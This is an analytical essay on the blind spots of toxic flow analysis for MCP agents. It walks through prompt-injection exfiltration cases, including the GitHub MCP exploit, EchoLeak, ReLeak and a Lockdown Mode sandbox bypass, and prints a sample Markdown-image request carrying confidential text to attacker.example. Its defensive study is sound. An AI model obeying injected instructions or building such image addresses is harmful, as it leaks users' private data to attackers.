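# Data leaks that tool-graph analysis of AI agents cannot represent

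## Tool graphs and the labels put on them

Toxic flow analysis is a method for finding ways an attacker could steal data through an AI agent. A scanner lists the agent's tools, labels each one by the part it could play in a theft, and raises a warning when the labeled tools form a complete route from the attacker's text to the private data and out again. Invariant Labs, a security company now owned by Snyk, published the method in July 2025. Because the method covers only tools, it cannot represent data leaving by other means, such as through a chat window that loads an image from the web or a person who clicks a link.

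### Agents, tools and the Model Context Protocol

A language model on its own only produces text. In an office example from *MCP 2026 changes the rules* (Granados, 2026), the model suggests a list of steps, and the user opens the calendar, finds the document and sends the email by hand. An agent is a language model that can take such steps itself using tools, which are functions that ordinary software offers to the model, such as one for reading mail or one for fetching a web page.

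The Model Context Protocol (MCP), which Anthropic introduced in 2024, is an open standard for connecting AI applications to tools and outside data. By July 2026, developers were downloading its main software kits close to half a billion times a month, according to the release announcement from Model Context Protocol (2026).

The current specification, Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), describes how a call works. A server, the program that offers the tools, supplies a list of them on request. Each entry has a name, a plain-language description and a schema for the inputs. The client, the program in which a person uses the agent, such as a chat window or code editor, passes the list to the model. When the model selects a tool, it writes the tool's name and arguments. The client sends the call to the server, the server returns a result, and the client adds the result to the text the model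 is working on. The model then selects the next step, and no programmer has fixed the order of the calls in advance. The specification recommends, but does not require, that a person always be able to refuse a call.

### Why text from outside can steer an agent

Tool results are a security problem because they enter the same stream of text as the user's request. Prompt injection is text from an outsider that the model treats as an instruction. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a recruiter's system that scores applicants' CVs. A candidate hides a line in the CV telling the system to approve it, and the model may act on the line as though the recruiter had written it. The candidate does this without access to the system, and an attacker can target an agent with a mail tool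 in the same way, since anyone can send an email.

The name "prompt injection" comes from SQL injection, an attack in which text from a web form runs as a database command. Developers can reliably prevent SQL injection with parameterized queries, which fix the structure of the command before the user's text is added. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) explains why this remedy does not carry over to prompt injection. Natural language has no grammar that lets a parser tell commands from data, as SQL's does, and models are trained to follow instructions wherever they appear.

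Developers mark each passage in the stream with a role, such as "user" or "tool". *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) found that models infer the source of a passage from how it sounds rather than from that mark. *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* (2026) proves that perfect prevention of prompt injection is impossible in a model that maps instructions and data into one space of representations with no enforced separation between them. The proof does not apply to architectures that enforce such a separation, and it does not establish how often a given attack succeeds. That rate has to be measured, and it differs a great deal from model to model.

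David C concludes that designers should assume an attacker can confuse the model, and should estimate the damage as if they had given the attacker direct access to the agent's tools. A security review can then start from the tools, however well the model resists attack.

### From the lethal trifecta to rule TF001

Much of the field has adopted an account of which tools are dangerous together from Simon Willison, the software developer who coined the term prompt injection. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) named three capabilities that together let an attacker steal data: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. If any one is missing, the theft fails, because the attacker's instruction never reaches the agent, there is nothing worth stealing, or the agent has no way to send the data out.

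Willison had collected dozens of such attacks on commercial products. The vendors promptly fixed almost all of them, usually by blocking the route through which data could leave. A user who connects tools from several sources has no vendor to do this, and MCP makes it easy to combine tools this way. In a post on tool labels, Model Context Protocol (2026) described the risk as "a property of the session, not of any single server", where a session is one conversation or task.

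Toxic flow analysis is a search based on the trifecta, which Snyk Labs describes in two steps. The first step is to build a flow graph of the agent system, in which the nodes are tools and the edges are possible sequences of calls. Each tool has properties that record how far to trust it, how sensitive its data are, and whether it could be used for exfiltration, the transfer of private data to someone not entitled to it. The second step is to search the graph for toxic flows, which are tool sequences that would violate security if the agent ran them, and score them. The analysis looks at sequences because there may be nothing wrong with any single tool in a toxic flow. Snyk's *Understanding Toxic Flows in MCP and the Hidden Risk of AI-Native Systems* points out that filters examine single prompts and access reviews examine single tools, while the breach comes from the combination.

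The scanner's rule for data theft has the code TF001. Invariant Labs' *Issue Code Reference* defines it by three roles:

- An **untrusted-content tool** is one whose output could be malicious, such as a tool that fetches a web page set up by someone else.
- A **private-data tool** exposes private data to the agent, for example by reading a file on the user's machine.
- A **public sink** is a tool through which the agent can send information back to the attacker. It may do so with a message to an arbitrary phone number, or by making the information public.

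One tool may fill several roles, or all three. Each tool therefore gets a set of labels, which may be empty. Let t₁, …, tₙ be the tools connected to one agent, and let λ(t) be the subset of {untrusted, private, sink} that belongs to tool t. The alarm sounds when

λ(t₁) ∪ λ(t₂) ∪ … ∪ λ(tₙ) = {untrusted, private, sink}.

In the attack, the agent reads the attacker's text, then fetches the private data, then sends that data out. The formula can ignore this order as long as the model is free to call any tool after any other. The graph then has an edge between every pair of tools, so a path through the three roles exists whenever all three labels are present. Connecting another tool can therefore trigger the alarm but can never turn it off.

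A warning under TF001 means that theft is possible with these tools, but doesn't indicate how likely it is. The absence of a warning would rule out theft only if the analysis were sound, meaning it raised a warning for every leak possible within its stated scope. A companion rule, TF002, covers damage instead of theft. It needs only two roles: an untrusted-content tool and a destructive tool, which can do something irreversible such as deleting a file or sending money.

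### The GitHub exploit as a path through the graph

Two months before the method was published, Marco Milanta and Luca Beurer-Kellner demonstrated an attack that fits the rule exactly, in Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025). GitHub hosts code in public and private repositories, and its official MCP server lets an agent work with both. They set up a demonstration account with several private repositories and one public one, a simple Pacman game. Anyone on GitHub can file an issue, such as a bug report, on a public repository, and the researchers filed one containing an injected instruction.

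The account owner then asked Claude 4 Opus, through Claude Desktop, to look at the open issues. The agent read the planted issue and followed its instructions. It fetched data from the private repositories and put them into a pull request (a proposed code change) on the public repository. Anyone could read the pull request, which revealed the name of a private project, the owner's plan to move to South America and the owner's salary.

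| Step | What the tool does | Label | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Lists the issues of a public repository | untrusted | The attacker's text reaches the model |
| 2 | Reads a private repository | private | Private data join the same text |
| 3 | Opens a pull request on a public repository | sink | Anyone can read the data |

Connecting the GitHub server alone is enough to produce all three labels, so the analysis raises the alarm before any attack. Nothing in the chain had malfunctioned. Invariant Labs attributed the fault to the agent system's architecture and concluded that GitHub could not fix it by patching the server. By default, Claude Desktop asks the user to confirm each call, but the researchers observed that many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching.

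The case is limited evidence for the method. Invariant Labs found the flow with its own analyzer and ran the attack on accounts it had created. This shows that the method can find a real flow in widely used software, but it does not establish a detection rate.

Invariant Labs proposed a rule, enforced while the agent runs, that limits the agent to one repository per session. This blocks the attack because the agent cannot move from the public repository to a private one. But the formula still raises an alarm, because the same tools are connected and have the same labels. Whether a GitHub tool returns private data or a stranger's text depends on the repository named in the call, and a label on the whole tool is too coarse to record that.

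GitHub later announced, in August 2025, that its server would scan tool calls on public repositories for secrets such as access tokens (GitHub, 2025). This blocks leaks of credentials, but most of what leaked in the demonstration, including a salary and a plan to move abroad, would presumably still get through.

### What the scanner reads

Invariant Labs released toxic flow analysis as an early preview in MCP-scan, a program Snyk now distributes as Agent Scan. According to Snyk, the program searches a computer's configuration files for agents, MCP servers and skills (packaged instructions for an agent), then connects to the servers and retrieves the tool descriptions. It runs some checks locally. For others, it sends the skills, agent applications, and tool names and descriptions to Snyk, according to the *Agent Scan* documentation. It does not store or log the contents or results of tool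 calls.

The labels therefore depend largely on what each server's developer has written about its tools. MCP itself adds little. A server may attach four standard hints to a tool: that it only reads, that it can destroy something, that repeating a call is safe, or that it interacts with an open world of outside entities. None of these marks a tool as holding private data. Clients must also treat the hints as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server, since a malicious server can attach false ones. Five proposals for new labels or related features were open in March 2026, including one from GitHub and OpenAI on trust and sensitivity. The Model Context Protocol post that lists them advises anyone who needs a guarantee against exfiltration to use network controls or sandboxing rather than rely on a hint.

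The best available figures on the accuracy of labels based on tool descriptions come from *Parasites in the Toolchain* (Zhao, Hou and colleagues, 2025), a census that used the same three roles under other names. It collected 12,230 tools from 1,360 public MCP servers and had a language model assign roles from each tool's description and input schema. Three human reviewers then checked the assignments. Judged against their decisions, 85.5% of the roles the model assigned were correct, and it found 98.0% of the roles it should have assigned. It did worst on private-data tools, missing about one in 24. These scores are good, but the reviewers also worked from the descriptions, along with the model's own reasoning, so the scores show agreement about a text, which is weaker evidence than agreement about what a tool does when it runs.

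Zhao and colleagues therefore also ran the tools. Of the 5,666 that looked risky from their descriptions, 1,062 showed a risky capability in practice, or 8.7% of the whole collection. The rest cannot all be counted as false alarms, because about 30% of the servers required accounts with outside services that were hard to obtain, and others failed to run.

Only two of the 1,062 confirmed tools filled all three roles alone, and only two servers in the collection covered all three. Scanning one server at a time would therefore raise no alert in nearly every case, which is a strong argument for labeling all the tools connected to an agent together. The researchers tested such combinations with ten sets of three tools, nine of which combined tools from different servers. They planted an instruction in outside content and let Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent, run without confirmation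 prompts. Nine of the ten sets leaked private data at least once in ten attempts, and 36 of the 100 attempts succeeded. The set that never leaked combined a web scraper, a work-planning board and a tool for creating folders in a music collection. Their functions were so unrelated that the model did not chain them.

TF001 would have raised the same alarm for all ten sets of tools. It would also have raised the same alarm for every model, because its formula has no term for the model. In a second experiment on a single set of tools, every attempt failed against GPT-5 and Claude Sonnet 4.5, while most succeeded against DeepSeek-R1 and Gemini 2.5 Flash. Newer models have since replaced all four, but that would not change TF001's result.

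The consultancy Thoughtworks described toxic flow analysis as "still in its early stages" in *Toxic flow analysis for AI* (2025). In the 2026 update of that entry, Thoughtworks calls it a primary technique for finding unsafe data paths but keeps it in the category "Assess".

The toxic flow analysis framework can also use more kinds of data than the scanner, Agent Scan. Invariant Labs describes the framework as hybrid, meaning that it can use both static information about an agent's tools and servers and data captured while the agent runs. A record of actual calls would include the repository that an agent read, which no tool description can supply. An objection to labels drawn from descriptions therefore applies to Agent Scan but not automatically to the framework. Snyk has put its runtime protection into a separate product, Agent Guard, which was in private preview in March 2026, when Agent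 Scan was in open preview (Snyk, 2026).

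## What it means for a flow to fall outside the graph

A scanner can miss a leak because a tool has the wrong label or because the tool graph cannot represent the leak. Correcting labels fixes the first problem, but it doesn't help the scanner detect data that leave through something other than a tool.

### Soundness, and three ways to fail

A program analysis is sound if its result covers everything the program could do when it runs. *In Defense of Soundiness* (Livshits, Sridharan and colleagues, 2015) gives this definition and explains that a sound analysis has to overestimate to keep the computation manageable, so it also reports behavior that never occurs. A precise analysis reports little such behavior.

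A more general definition comes from Smaragdakis, in *From Soundiness to Soundness*: an analysis is sound if whatever it claims is true. For a leak scanner, the claim that matters is the one an operator takes from a clean result, namely that private data cannot get out. Soundness then requires, for every system x:

x can leak by a route within the stated scope ⇒ the analysis raises an alarm on x.

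TF001, the scanner's rule for data theft, allows for any order of calls and any injected instruction. So if the labels are correct, it catches every theft in which the injection arrives in a tool's output and the same agent sends the data out in a tool call. It can miss other leaks for three reasons.

A tool may be in the graph but lack the label for a role it has, like the private-data tools that the model missed in the census by Zhao and colleagues. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) describes a subtler case in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. The program asked for human approval before running many shell commands that could send data to unknown domains, but it let `ping` run without approval. Before `ping` contacts a machine, the computer looks up the machine's name on the network, and an attacker can have the agent put stolen data in that name. Anyone who knew this would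 have treated `ping` as a command that can send data out.

A label may also be too coarse, like those on the GitHub server's tools, which stay the same whichever repository the agent reads. This usually causes false alarms, but an operator who tires of them may delete the label, which leaves the tool mislabeled.

Finally, the graph may have no node or edge for the flow. One way to distinguish this from a labeling problem is to suppose that someone with complete knowledge of the tools corrected every label, and even gave each possible call its own label. The problem was in the labels if the analysis would now raise an alarm, but if data could still get out undetected, the graph cannot represent the flow and better labels won't help.

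### An assistant with two tools

Consider an office assistant that can read its user's mail and search the user's files. Anyone can send the user an email, so its tools have these labels:

λ(read_mail) = {untrusted, private}

λ(search_files) = {private}

Together, the agent's tools have the labels {untrusted, private}. There is no public sink, so TF001 raises no warning. Both labels are correct, and finer labels would not change the result. An attacker can send an email that persuades the agent to collect confidential files, but the agent has no tool for sending them to the attacker.

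The assistant does not run in isolation, though. Around it are four things that the graph leaves out:

- a chat window that renders the assistant's replies, meaning that it turns the text into a displayed page and loads any image the text names
- a memory, in which the assistant stores notes in one session and reads them in a later one
- a user, who clicks links and copies text into other programs
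- a second agent, which receives the assistant's summaries as input and has a tool for posting to a public website

An attacker can steal data through the chat window even when none of the agent's tool calls send anything out. Suppose the attacker's email tells the agent to find a certain file and to include in its reply an image whose address begins with attacker.example and continues with text from the file. The agent calls read_mail and search_files, as it is allowed to do, and writes the reply. The chat window then requests the image at that address, which sends the text from the file to the attacker's server.

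### Three tests for a missing flow

Three questions show whether a graph can represent a given leak:

- **Sender:** does the component that sends the request appear as a node?
- **Carrier:** does whatever carries the data appear as an edge?
- **Time:** does the graph cover the time at which the leak happens?

The image fails the sender test because the chat window, which is not a tool, sends the request. In the `ping` case, the request also comes from another component, the part of the operating system that looks up names. But that lookup happens only because the agent ran a command, so a sink label on the shell tool can cover everything the command triggers. No label on a tool can cover the chat window's request in this way, because the chat window acts on the finished reply, after the last tool call.

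The second agent shows why the carrier test is necessary. Its posting tool is a node labeled {sink}, but it is in a different graph from the assistant's tools. An operator who scans each agent separately finds {untrusted, private} for the assistant and {sink} for the second agent, and neither set triggers an alarm. No edge connects the two graphs to represent the summary that carries the data across.

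A scan can miss a leak when the set of tools changes over time. Suppose that on Monday an injected email makes the assistant save a file's contents in its memory, with an instruction to publish them. By Thursday the operator has disconnected the email and file tools and connected a new one, post_page, which has the label {sink}. A scan on Monday finds two of the three roles and a scan on Thursday finds only the third, but the memory carries the file's contents and the instruction from one day to the other. If all three tools had been connected on either day, TF001 would have raised the alarm.

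| Route out | Sender is a node? | Carrier is an edge? | Time covered? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Chat window loads an image | No | No: the reply | Yes |
| Memory, then a tool connected later | Yes, in Thursday's graph | No: the stored note | No |
| User clicks a link or pastes text | No | No: the user | Only if it happens at once |
| Second agent posts a summary | Only in its own graph | No: the summary | Only if it runs in the same session |

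All four routes fail the carrier test, so it is the best test to apply if there is time for only one. The other two tests help an operator decide where to put a defense. If the sender is missing from the graph, the operator needs control over the requests that component makes, and if there is a gap in time, the operator needs a record that stays with the stored data.

Real attacks can combine these gaps. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* analyzes a case known as SpAIware, in which an injected instruction on a website or in a document got into the long-term memory of the ChatGPT app for macOS. Because the instruction stayed in memory across sessions, the app kept sending the user's conversations to the attacker. It sent them through its own rendering, by loading an invisible image with the text in its address.

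A related security principle, complete mediation, requires a check on every request that crosses a security boundary. Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2025), in *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing*, warn that enforcing a policy only on tool calls can leave gaps. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* draws the boundary more widely, around every interface through which an agent reaches or affects protected resources, including network communication and changes to stored state. Its guarantees hold only if the enforcement points together cover all of these interfaces and nothing can bypass them. For the two-tool assistant, the checks would also have to cover the image request and the write to memory.

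### Removing the last sink

Suppose the assistant originally had a third tool, send_mail, labeled {sink}. TF001 raised a warning, which was correct because the system could leak, even though the chat window was missing from the graph. If the operator then disconnects send_mail, the warning disappears. The chat window still loads images, so the system can still leak, and the scanner's result is now wrong.

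A flow falls outside the graph whenever the graph omits a way for data to leave. If the connected tools have all three labels, the scanner raises an alarm regardless of the omission. The omission changes the result only when the labels are incomplete, as they are in systems that someone has just repaired. An evaluation using only agents with plenty of labeled sinks would therefore never expose the problem, because the scanner would give the right answer every time.

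Removing the sink is an obvious repair, because an assistant for mail and files needs access to both but can often do without sending anything. Published descriptions of the attack also suggest this repair. Snyk Labs, explaining an attack on the code editor Cursor, writes that a toxic flow attack "relies on three conditions being met". The last is that the agent has a tool that can exfiltrate information, so a reader will naturally conclude that removing the tool prevents the attack.

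Willison's original third condition was broader, requiring only the ability to communicate externally. An assistant has that ability if its replies cause a chat window to contact any server on the internet, so his rule that the theft fails without it still holds for the two-tool assistant. The scanner replaces "ability" with "tool" because it can list only tools, and the rule no longer holds after that change.

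### Lampson's confinement problem

Computer scientists studied this problem long before language models existed. In *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, Lampson (1973) asked how a customer could run someone else's program on confidential data and be sure that it would not pass the data to the program's owner. He pointed out that a customer who gets bad results can see them, but generally has no evidence when data leaks.

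In Lampson's setting, the program's owner is the hostile party. An agent's developer usually means no harm, but an outsider whose prompt injection succeeds gains much the same control over what the agent does with the data.

Lampson listed seven ways a program can leak data. The program can remember the data until its owner calls it, write to a permanent file, share a temporary file, or send a message to another process. It can encode information in the bill for its services, since the owner must receive a copy. It can signal one bit at a time by opening and closing files that another program is also trying to open. It can vary how heavily it uses the computer, while another program measures the slowdown. Lampson sorted these into three kinds of channel. Storage channels use something that one program can write and another can read. Legitimate channels, such as the bill, are outputs the program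 is supposed to produce. Covert channels, such as the load on the computer, were never intended to carry information.

An image request is ordinary network traffic, and the reply that causes it is a legitimate output, like the bill. A scanner that misses the request shouldn't be excused on the grounds that the channel is covert. The assistant's memory is a storage channel. Early researchers considered both kinds of channel manageable. According to lecture slides from Purdue University, Steven Lipner concluded in a 1975 comment on Lampson's paper that system designers could close storage and legitimate channels with little loss of efficiency, but that closing covert channels seemed to carry an unreasonable performance penalty.

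The features around the assistant conflict with two of Lampson's rules. A confined program must be memoryless, meaning it cannot keep information from one call to the next, and the assistant's memory breaks this rule. If a confined program calls a program that the customer does not trust, that program must be confined too. Handing summaries to an unconfined second agent goes against the intent of this rule.

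### From channels to data

Denning (1976), in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, put labels on data. Her model contains storage objects, such as files and variables, and processes that move information between them. Each object belongs to a security class. An arrow from one class to another means that information may flow that way, and an operator ⊕ gives the class of anything computed from several inputs. When a process computes a value from objects a₁, …, aₙ and puts it in object b, security requires that

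class(a₁) ⊕ … ⊕ class(aₙ) → class(b).

Under certain natural assumptions, the classes form a lattice, a structure in which any two classes have a lowest class above both. ⊕ returns that class, so combined data is at least as restricted as each of its sources.

With just two classes, public and confidential, the model can forbid any flow from confidential to public. The assistant's reply is confidential because it draws on a confidential file, and the attacker's server is public. When the chat window puts part of the reply into an image request, it moves confidential data to a public object, which the rule forbids. This holds whether or not the chat window counts as a tool. The model can also represent the stored notes and the user, since Denning allows a user to count as an object.

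She also showed how a label can get lost between two programs. Let a be a secret value, either true or false, and let c be a variable that both programs can use. The first program sets c to false and then, if a is false, changes c to true. The second program sets b to false and then, if c is false, changes b to true. At the end b always equals a, but b still has the lowest label. When a is true, the first program reads the secret but does not change c, so c keeps its low label. The second program then starts with no record of what the first one read. Several systems of the time had this flaw, even though they never lowered a running program's label. An agent's memory can serve as c. In the Monday and Thursday example the leak is cruder, because the note contains the secret itself, but the record of where the secret came from is lost in the same place.

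Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*, began with the observer. One group of users does not interfere with another if nothing the first group does affects what the second group sees. The same definition works for a set of commands. Let w be any history of commands, let p(w) be the same history with the commands in question struck out, and let wᵤ be what user u sees after w. There is no interference with u if, for every w,

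wᵤ = p(w)ᵤ.

To apply this to the assistant, let the commands be the ones that saved the private files, and let u be the attacker. After the theft, the attacker's server log contains text from a file. Strike out the command that saved the file, and the log is different. The system therefore fails, and the test required no list of the routes by which the text might have traveled. (Goguen and Meseguer's machine always gives the same output for the same history. A language model may not, so a careful version would compare the probabilities of what the attacker sees.)

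Noninterference still requires someone to specify what the attacker can see. Goguen and Meseguer assume that their model includes all the information the system gives each user. They note that users can presumably learn things in other ways, but they do not try to describe them. If the model of the assistant omits the attacker's server log, the assistant passes even if it leaks data through that log. Noninterference replaces a list of exits with a list of observations, which is usually shorter for an outside attacker, but an incomplete list of either kind gives a false result.

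### Why not just add a node?

These leaks fall outside the graph because all its nodes are tools. A graph that also included other kinds of nodes could represent any of them. For example, adding the chat window to the assistant's graph with the label {sink} would complete the three roles, and TF001 would raise an alert.

The first difficulty is finding out what to add to the graph. Lampson thought a trustworthy system had to block every channel, but that there was unlikely to be a rigorous way to identify them all in even a moderately complex system. Lipner thought identifying all the storage objects was difficult but possible. Lipner's view seems reasonable for one assistant in one known chat window, but it is harder to defend for a product that gains new features every few weeks.

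A scanner also needs evidence about each node, and tool descriptions do not record whether the chat window loads images from unknown servers. Snyk's Agent Scan already recognizes 13 agent programs, including Cursor and Claude Desktop, by where they are installed. Snyk could get some of the missing information by keeping a table of how each program handles images, though it would have to track every new version and setting.

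The more serious problem is lost precision. If every chat window counts as a sink, the sink label is always present, and TF001 raises an alarm whenever an agent has untrusted content and private data. The tool read_mail has both, so every assistant that reads mail would always trigger the alarm. Livshits and colleagues report the same problem in ordinary program analysis, where modeling every language feature soundly usually destroys precision. Goguen and Meseguer likewise objected to methods that trace everything that could "potentially" flow, because such methods leave the analyst with many cases that cannot occur.

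An operator could not clear such an alarm, even by turning off image loading. The new node is useful only if its label depends on how the chat window is set up, so that a window that loads no outside images is not labeled a sink. To cover memory, the formula would also have to combine roles across sessions. These changes lead to a larger model than the tool graph.

### Does a warning tool have to be sound?

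The other defense of the scanner is that it was meant to give warnings, not promised to find every flow. Invariant Labs (2025) presented toxic flow analysis as a way to "detect and warn". Livshits and colleagues support this view. They know of no sound analysis that works on whole industrial programs in a mainstream language, and they count security analysis among the uses that can tolerate unsoundness. A scanner that finds the GitHub flow before an attacker does is worth having even if it misses other flows.

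Smaragdakis distinguishes a bug detector, which is meant to report only real problems, from a verifier, which is meant to report all of them. TF001 fits neither description well. It isn't a sound bug detector because it warns about combinations of tools that may never leak in practice, such as the one set that Zhao and colleagues failed to exploit. Like a verifier, it overestimates the leaks within its graph, but it doesn't cover the routes outside the graph that a verifier of the whole system would need to include.

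Livshits and colleagues call an analysis "soundy" if it overestimates most behavior and deliberately ignores a few features that experts know about. They require its developers to say clearly what they have left out. The reference page for TF001 has no such list. It explains the theft with the sentence Invariant Labs wrote to introduce the three roles, "For this to work, three components are required". Anyone who takes that literally will conclude that theft is impossible with only two. Smaragdakis observes that an analysis's claim often exists only in the mind of its user, but here the documentation's wording leads the user to that claim.

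So the defense works when people act on the scanner's warnings, but fails when an operator treats the lack of a warning as permission to connect more private data. A short statement of scope would help that operator and take little effort to add. Denning gave one in 1976, when she wrote that her model would not deal with covert channels. For the two-tool assistant, a clean result could read, "The scan found no complete route among this agent's current tools. It did not check the chat window, memory, users or other agents."

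## Images and pages that a client program loads by itself

The chat window gives an attacker the shortest way out of the two-tool assistant, because it loads any image that a reply names.

### How an image address carries data

Many chat products display replies in Markdown, a notation that uses punctuation marks to indicate headings, links and images. To place an image in a reply, the model writes an exclamation mark, a short description and a web address. When the client renders the reply, it requests the picture from the server at that address.

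Suppose the assistant's user keeps a file about a planned takeover of a company called Heron. An attacker sends the user an email containing an injected instruction, and the theft takes five steps:

1. The user asks for a summary of the day's mail. The agent calls read_mail, and the attacker's text arrives with the other messages.
2. The agent follows the instruction and calls search_files. The file gives the offer price as 41 million.
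3. The agent writes the summary and adds an image at the end. The image's address begins with the name of the attacker's server and continues with words from the file.
4. The chat window renders the summary and requests the image.
5. The attacker's server logs the request, and the attacker reads the log.

The request in step 4 looks like this:

```
GET /logo.png?d=Heron%20offer%2041%20million HTTP/1.1
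Host: attacker.example
```

The first line names the requested picture, and the second names the server. The text after the question mark gives the server extra information, and %20 stands for a space. Websites commonly use this text for details such as a picture's size. The server doesn't need to have the picture, because it receives the data as soon as the request arrives. If it responds with a single transparent pixel, the user sees an ordinary summary.

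Only steps 1 and 2 involve tool calls, so the tool graph ends before the data leaves, and TF001 raises no warning.

A defense has to examine image addresses or the requests they cause. Searching replies for confidential text would not solve the problem, because the user is entitled to see the price and a correct answer to a question about Heron would include it. The same text is harmless in a sentence but leaks when it is part of an image address.

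### From pasted text to an unread email

Roman Samoilenko demonstrated the attack on ChatGPT in the spring of 2023. *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* (Willison, 2023) describes how a website added instructions to whatever text a visitor copied from it. When the visitor pasted the text into ChatGPT, the model put data from the chat into the address of a one-pixel image. The attack needed no tools, so it could work on a system whose tool graph was empty. OpenAI began to mitigate the problem in December 2023, eight months after Willison's post. Researchers kept finding ways to steal data from ChatGPT. Tenable's *HackedGPT* lists seven vulnerabilities and attack techniques, including theft of personal information and a bypass of safety mechanisms.

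Samoilenko's attack required the victim to paste the attacker's text, but EchoLeak, an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, needed only an email. Copilot is an assistant built into programs such as Word, Outlook and Teams. When a user asks a question, it retrieves related material from the user's mail, chats and files and adds it to the model's input. That material can include an attacker's email.

Aim Labs, a security research team, reported EchoLeak to Microsoft in January 2025 and published it that June. CyberInsider's *EchoLeak exploit enables silent data theft from Microsoft 365 Copilot* describes an attack that combines prompt injection, ways around Copilot's guardrails and creative Markdown formatting. The researchers called it the first zero-click vulnerability found in an AI product, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*. A zero-click attack needs no action by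 the victim beyond normal use. Willison (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, instead summarizes the theft as a link that leaks data when someone clicks it. The difference matters for defense because a user can choose not to click a link, but a client loads an image automatically.

Microsoft fixed the flaw and said that no attacker had obtained sensitive user data, according to Windows Central's *Microsoft Copilot's own default configuration exposed users*.

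### ReLeak

A year later, on December 3, 2026, the same team disclosed three more zero-click attacks on Copilot in *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026). The team is now called Cato AI Labs, after the network security company Cato Networks bought its parent. Each attack began with an email that the victim did not have to open. When the victim later asked Copilot an ordinary question, Copilot retrieved the email and the model followed the instructions hidden in it.

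Microsoft's filter against this kind of injection failed to block any of the three attacks. Punto Informatico's *ReLeak* explains that Copilot did not carry out direct commands from an email but accepted instructions that looked like legitimate requests. The researchers used AI agents to find wording that worked. According to Antipov's *Письмо даже не нужно открывать* (2026), the agents wrote test scenarios, analyzed Copilot's refusals and adjusted the next attempts under human direction.

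After the injection, each attack used a different way out:

- **An image in the reply.** Copilot put confidential data into the address of a Markdown image. The user's browser loaded the image automatically, and Microsoft's search service, Bing, passed the request on to the attacker's server.
- **A link in a saved document.** Copilot created a Word, Excel, PowerPoint or PDF file containing a link with confidential data in its address. The file went into the user's online storage, where Microsoft's own background processing followed the link. In the team's tests, the requests arrived one to eight minutes after the chat had ended, and nobody had to open the file, as Pixel Magazine's *Três ataques zero-click ao Microsoft 365 Copilot já foram corrigidos* (2026) reports.
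- **Code that Copilot ran.** Copilot can write and run programs in a code interpreter, inside a sandbox meant to isolate them. The researchers got around the isolation and had a program send the data directly to an outside server. Microsoft's documentation had promised that the sandbox allowed no network traffic in or out.

Only the first attack lies entirely outside a tool graph. The agent does not call a tool to write its reply, so there is no tool to label as a sink for the image. The code interpreter is a tool. A scanner that relied on Microsoft's documentation would have wrongly left it without a sink label, but someone who knew about the flaw could have added one. Saving a document is a less obvious case, because the background service sends the request. But it does so only because the agent saved a file, so a sink label on the saving tool would cover the request, much as a sink label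 on the shell tool covers the name lookup caused by `ping`.

| Way out | What causes the request | Could a tool label cover it? | Date of fix in 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Image in the reply | The browser loads the image through Bing | No | November 15 |
| Link in a saved document | Microsoft's background processing follows the link | Yes, on the tool that saves files | November 11 |
| Code that Copilot ran | The program itself contacts the server | Yes, on the code interpreter | September 17 |

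*An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) gives the dates for each fix. Cato reported the three flaws between July 29 and August 20, so Microsoft took at least 87 days to close the image route and at least 28 to close the interpreter route. Microsoft made the changes on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. Cato knew of no customers harmed by attackers.

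Faisal quotes the researchers as concluding that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak. Copilot still could not reliably tell outside content from legitimate instructions, and its new abilities to display images, write files and run code had each become a new way to leak data.

Cato sells security products for AI, so it has a commercial interest in this verdict, but the evidence supports it for images. The image attack worked against a product that Microsoft had already repaired once, and it used the same basic method that Samoilenko had shown three and a half years earlier. Microsoft could close a single route within weeks, as it did with the interpreter two months before ReLeak was made public, but the number of routes grew with the product. SearchLeak, another attack on Copilot described in June (Taler, 2026), also sent data through Bing, though it needed one click.

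### The preview that escaped Lockdown Mode

Besides loading images, the ChatGPT client can preview web pages that the model has written, and these pages may contain working code. In November 2026, the security company Check Point described how such a preview could get around Lockdown Mode, a ChatGPT setting meant to prevent this kind of data theft.

OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* presents Lockdown Mode as an optional setting for users at higher risk. It works on the last stage of an attack by limiting outgoing network requests that could carry sensitive data. OpenAI states that the mode does not stop injected instructions from appearing in the content ChatGPT reads. This approach follows David C's advice to assume that the model can be confused and to limit the damage. Willison (2026) concluded that if such a mode is necessary, ChatGPT's default settings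 do not robustly protect users against a determined attacker.

ChatGPT already placed the previewed page in a sandbox, which blocked its access to the application's cookies and stored data and kept it from contacting outside servers without the user's consent. The sandbox consisted of nested frames (pages displayed inside other pages), and the browser enforces a list of permissions for each frame.

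In The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026), Eli Smadja, Check Point's head of research, explained how a page previewed in ChatGPT could leak chat data despite Lockdown Mode. ChatGPT intercepted the page's direct attempts to open a new window, but the preview frame's permissions still allowed popups and let them run outside the sandbox. The page could create another frame inside itself and use that frame's unmodified copy of the function that opens windows. The preview's restrictions did not apply to the new window, so chat data could leave through it.

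An attacker could deliver the page through a crafted prompt, a shared chat or a malicious GPT (a customized version of ChatGPT). In the desktop application, the theft required no click. The attacker also controlled what the new window displayed and could show a fake update notice that led the user to malware. OpenAI fixed the flaw on September 18, 2026, before Check Point published it.

OpenAI had put its check on one function for opening windows, but the browser's popup permission governed every such function. Under the principle of complete mediation, the check belongs on the permission. Removing that permission would have blocked the extra frame as well as the original page.

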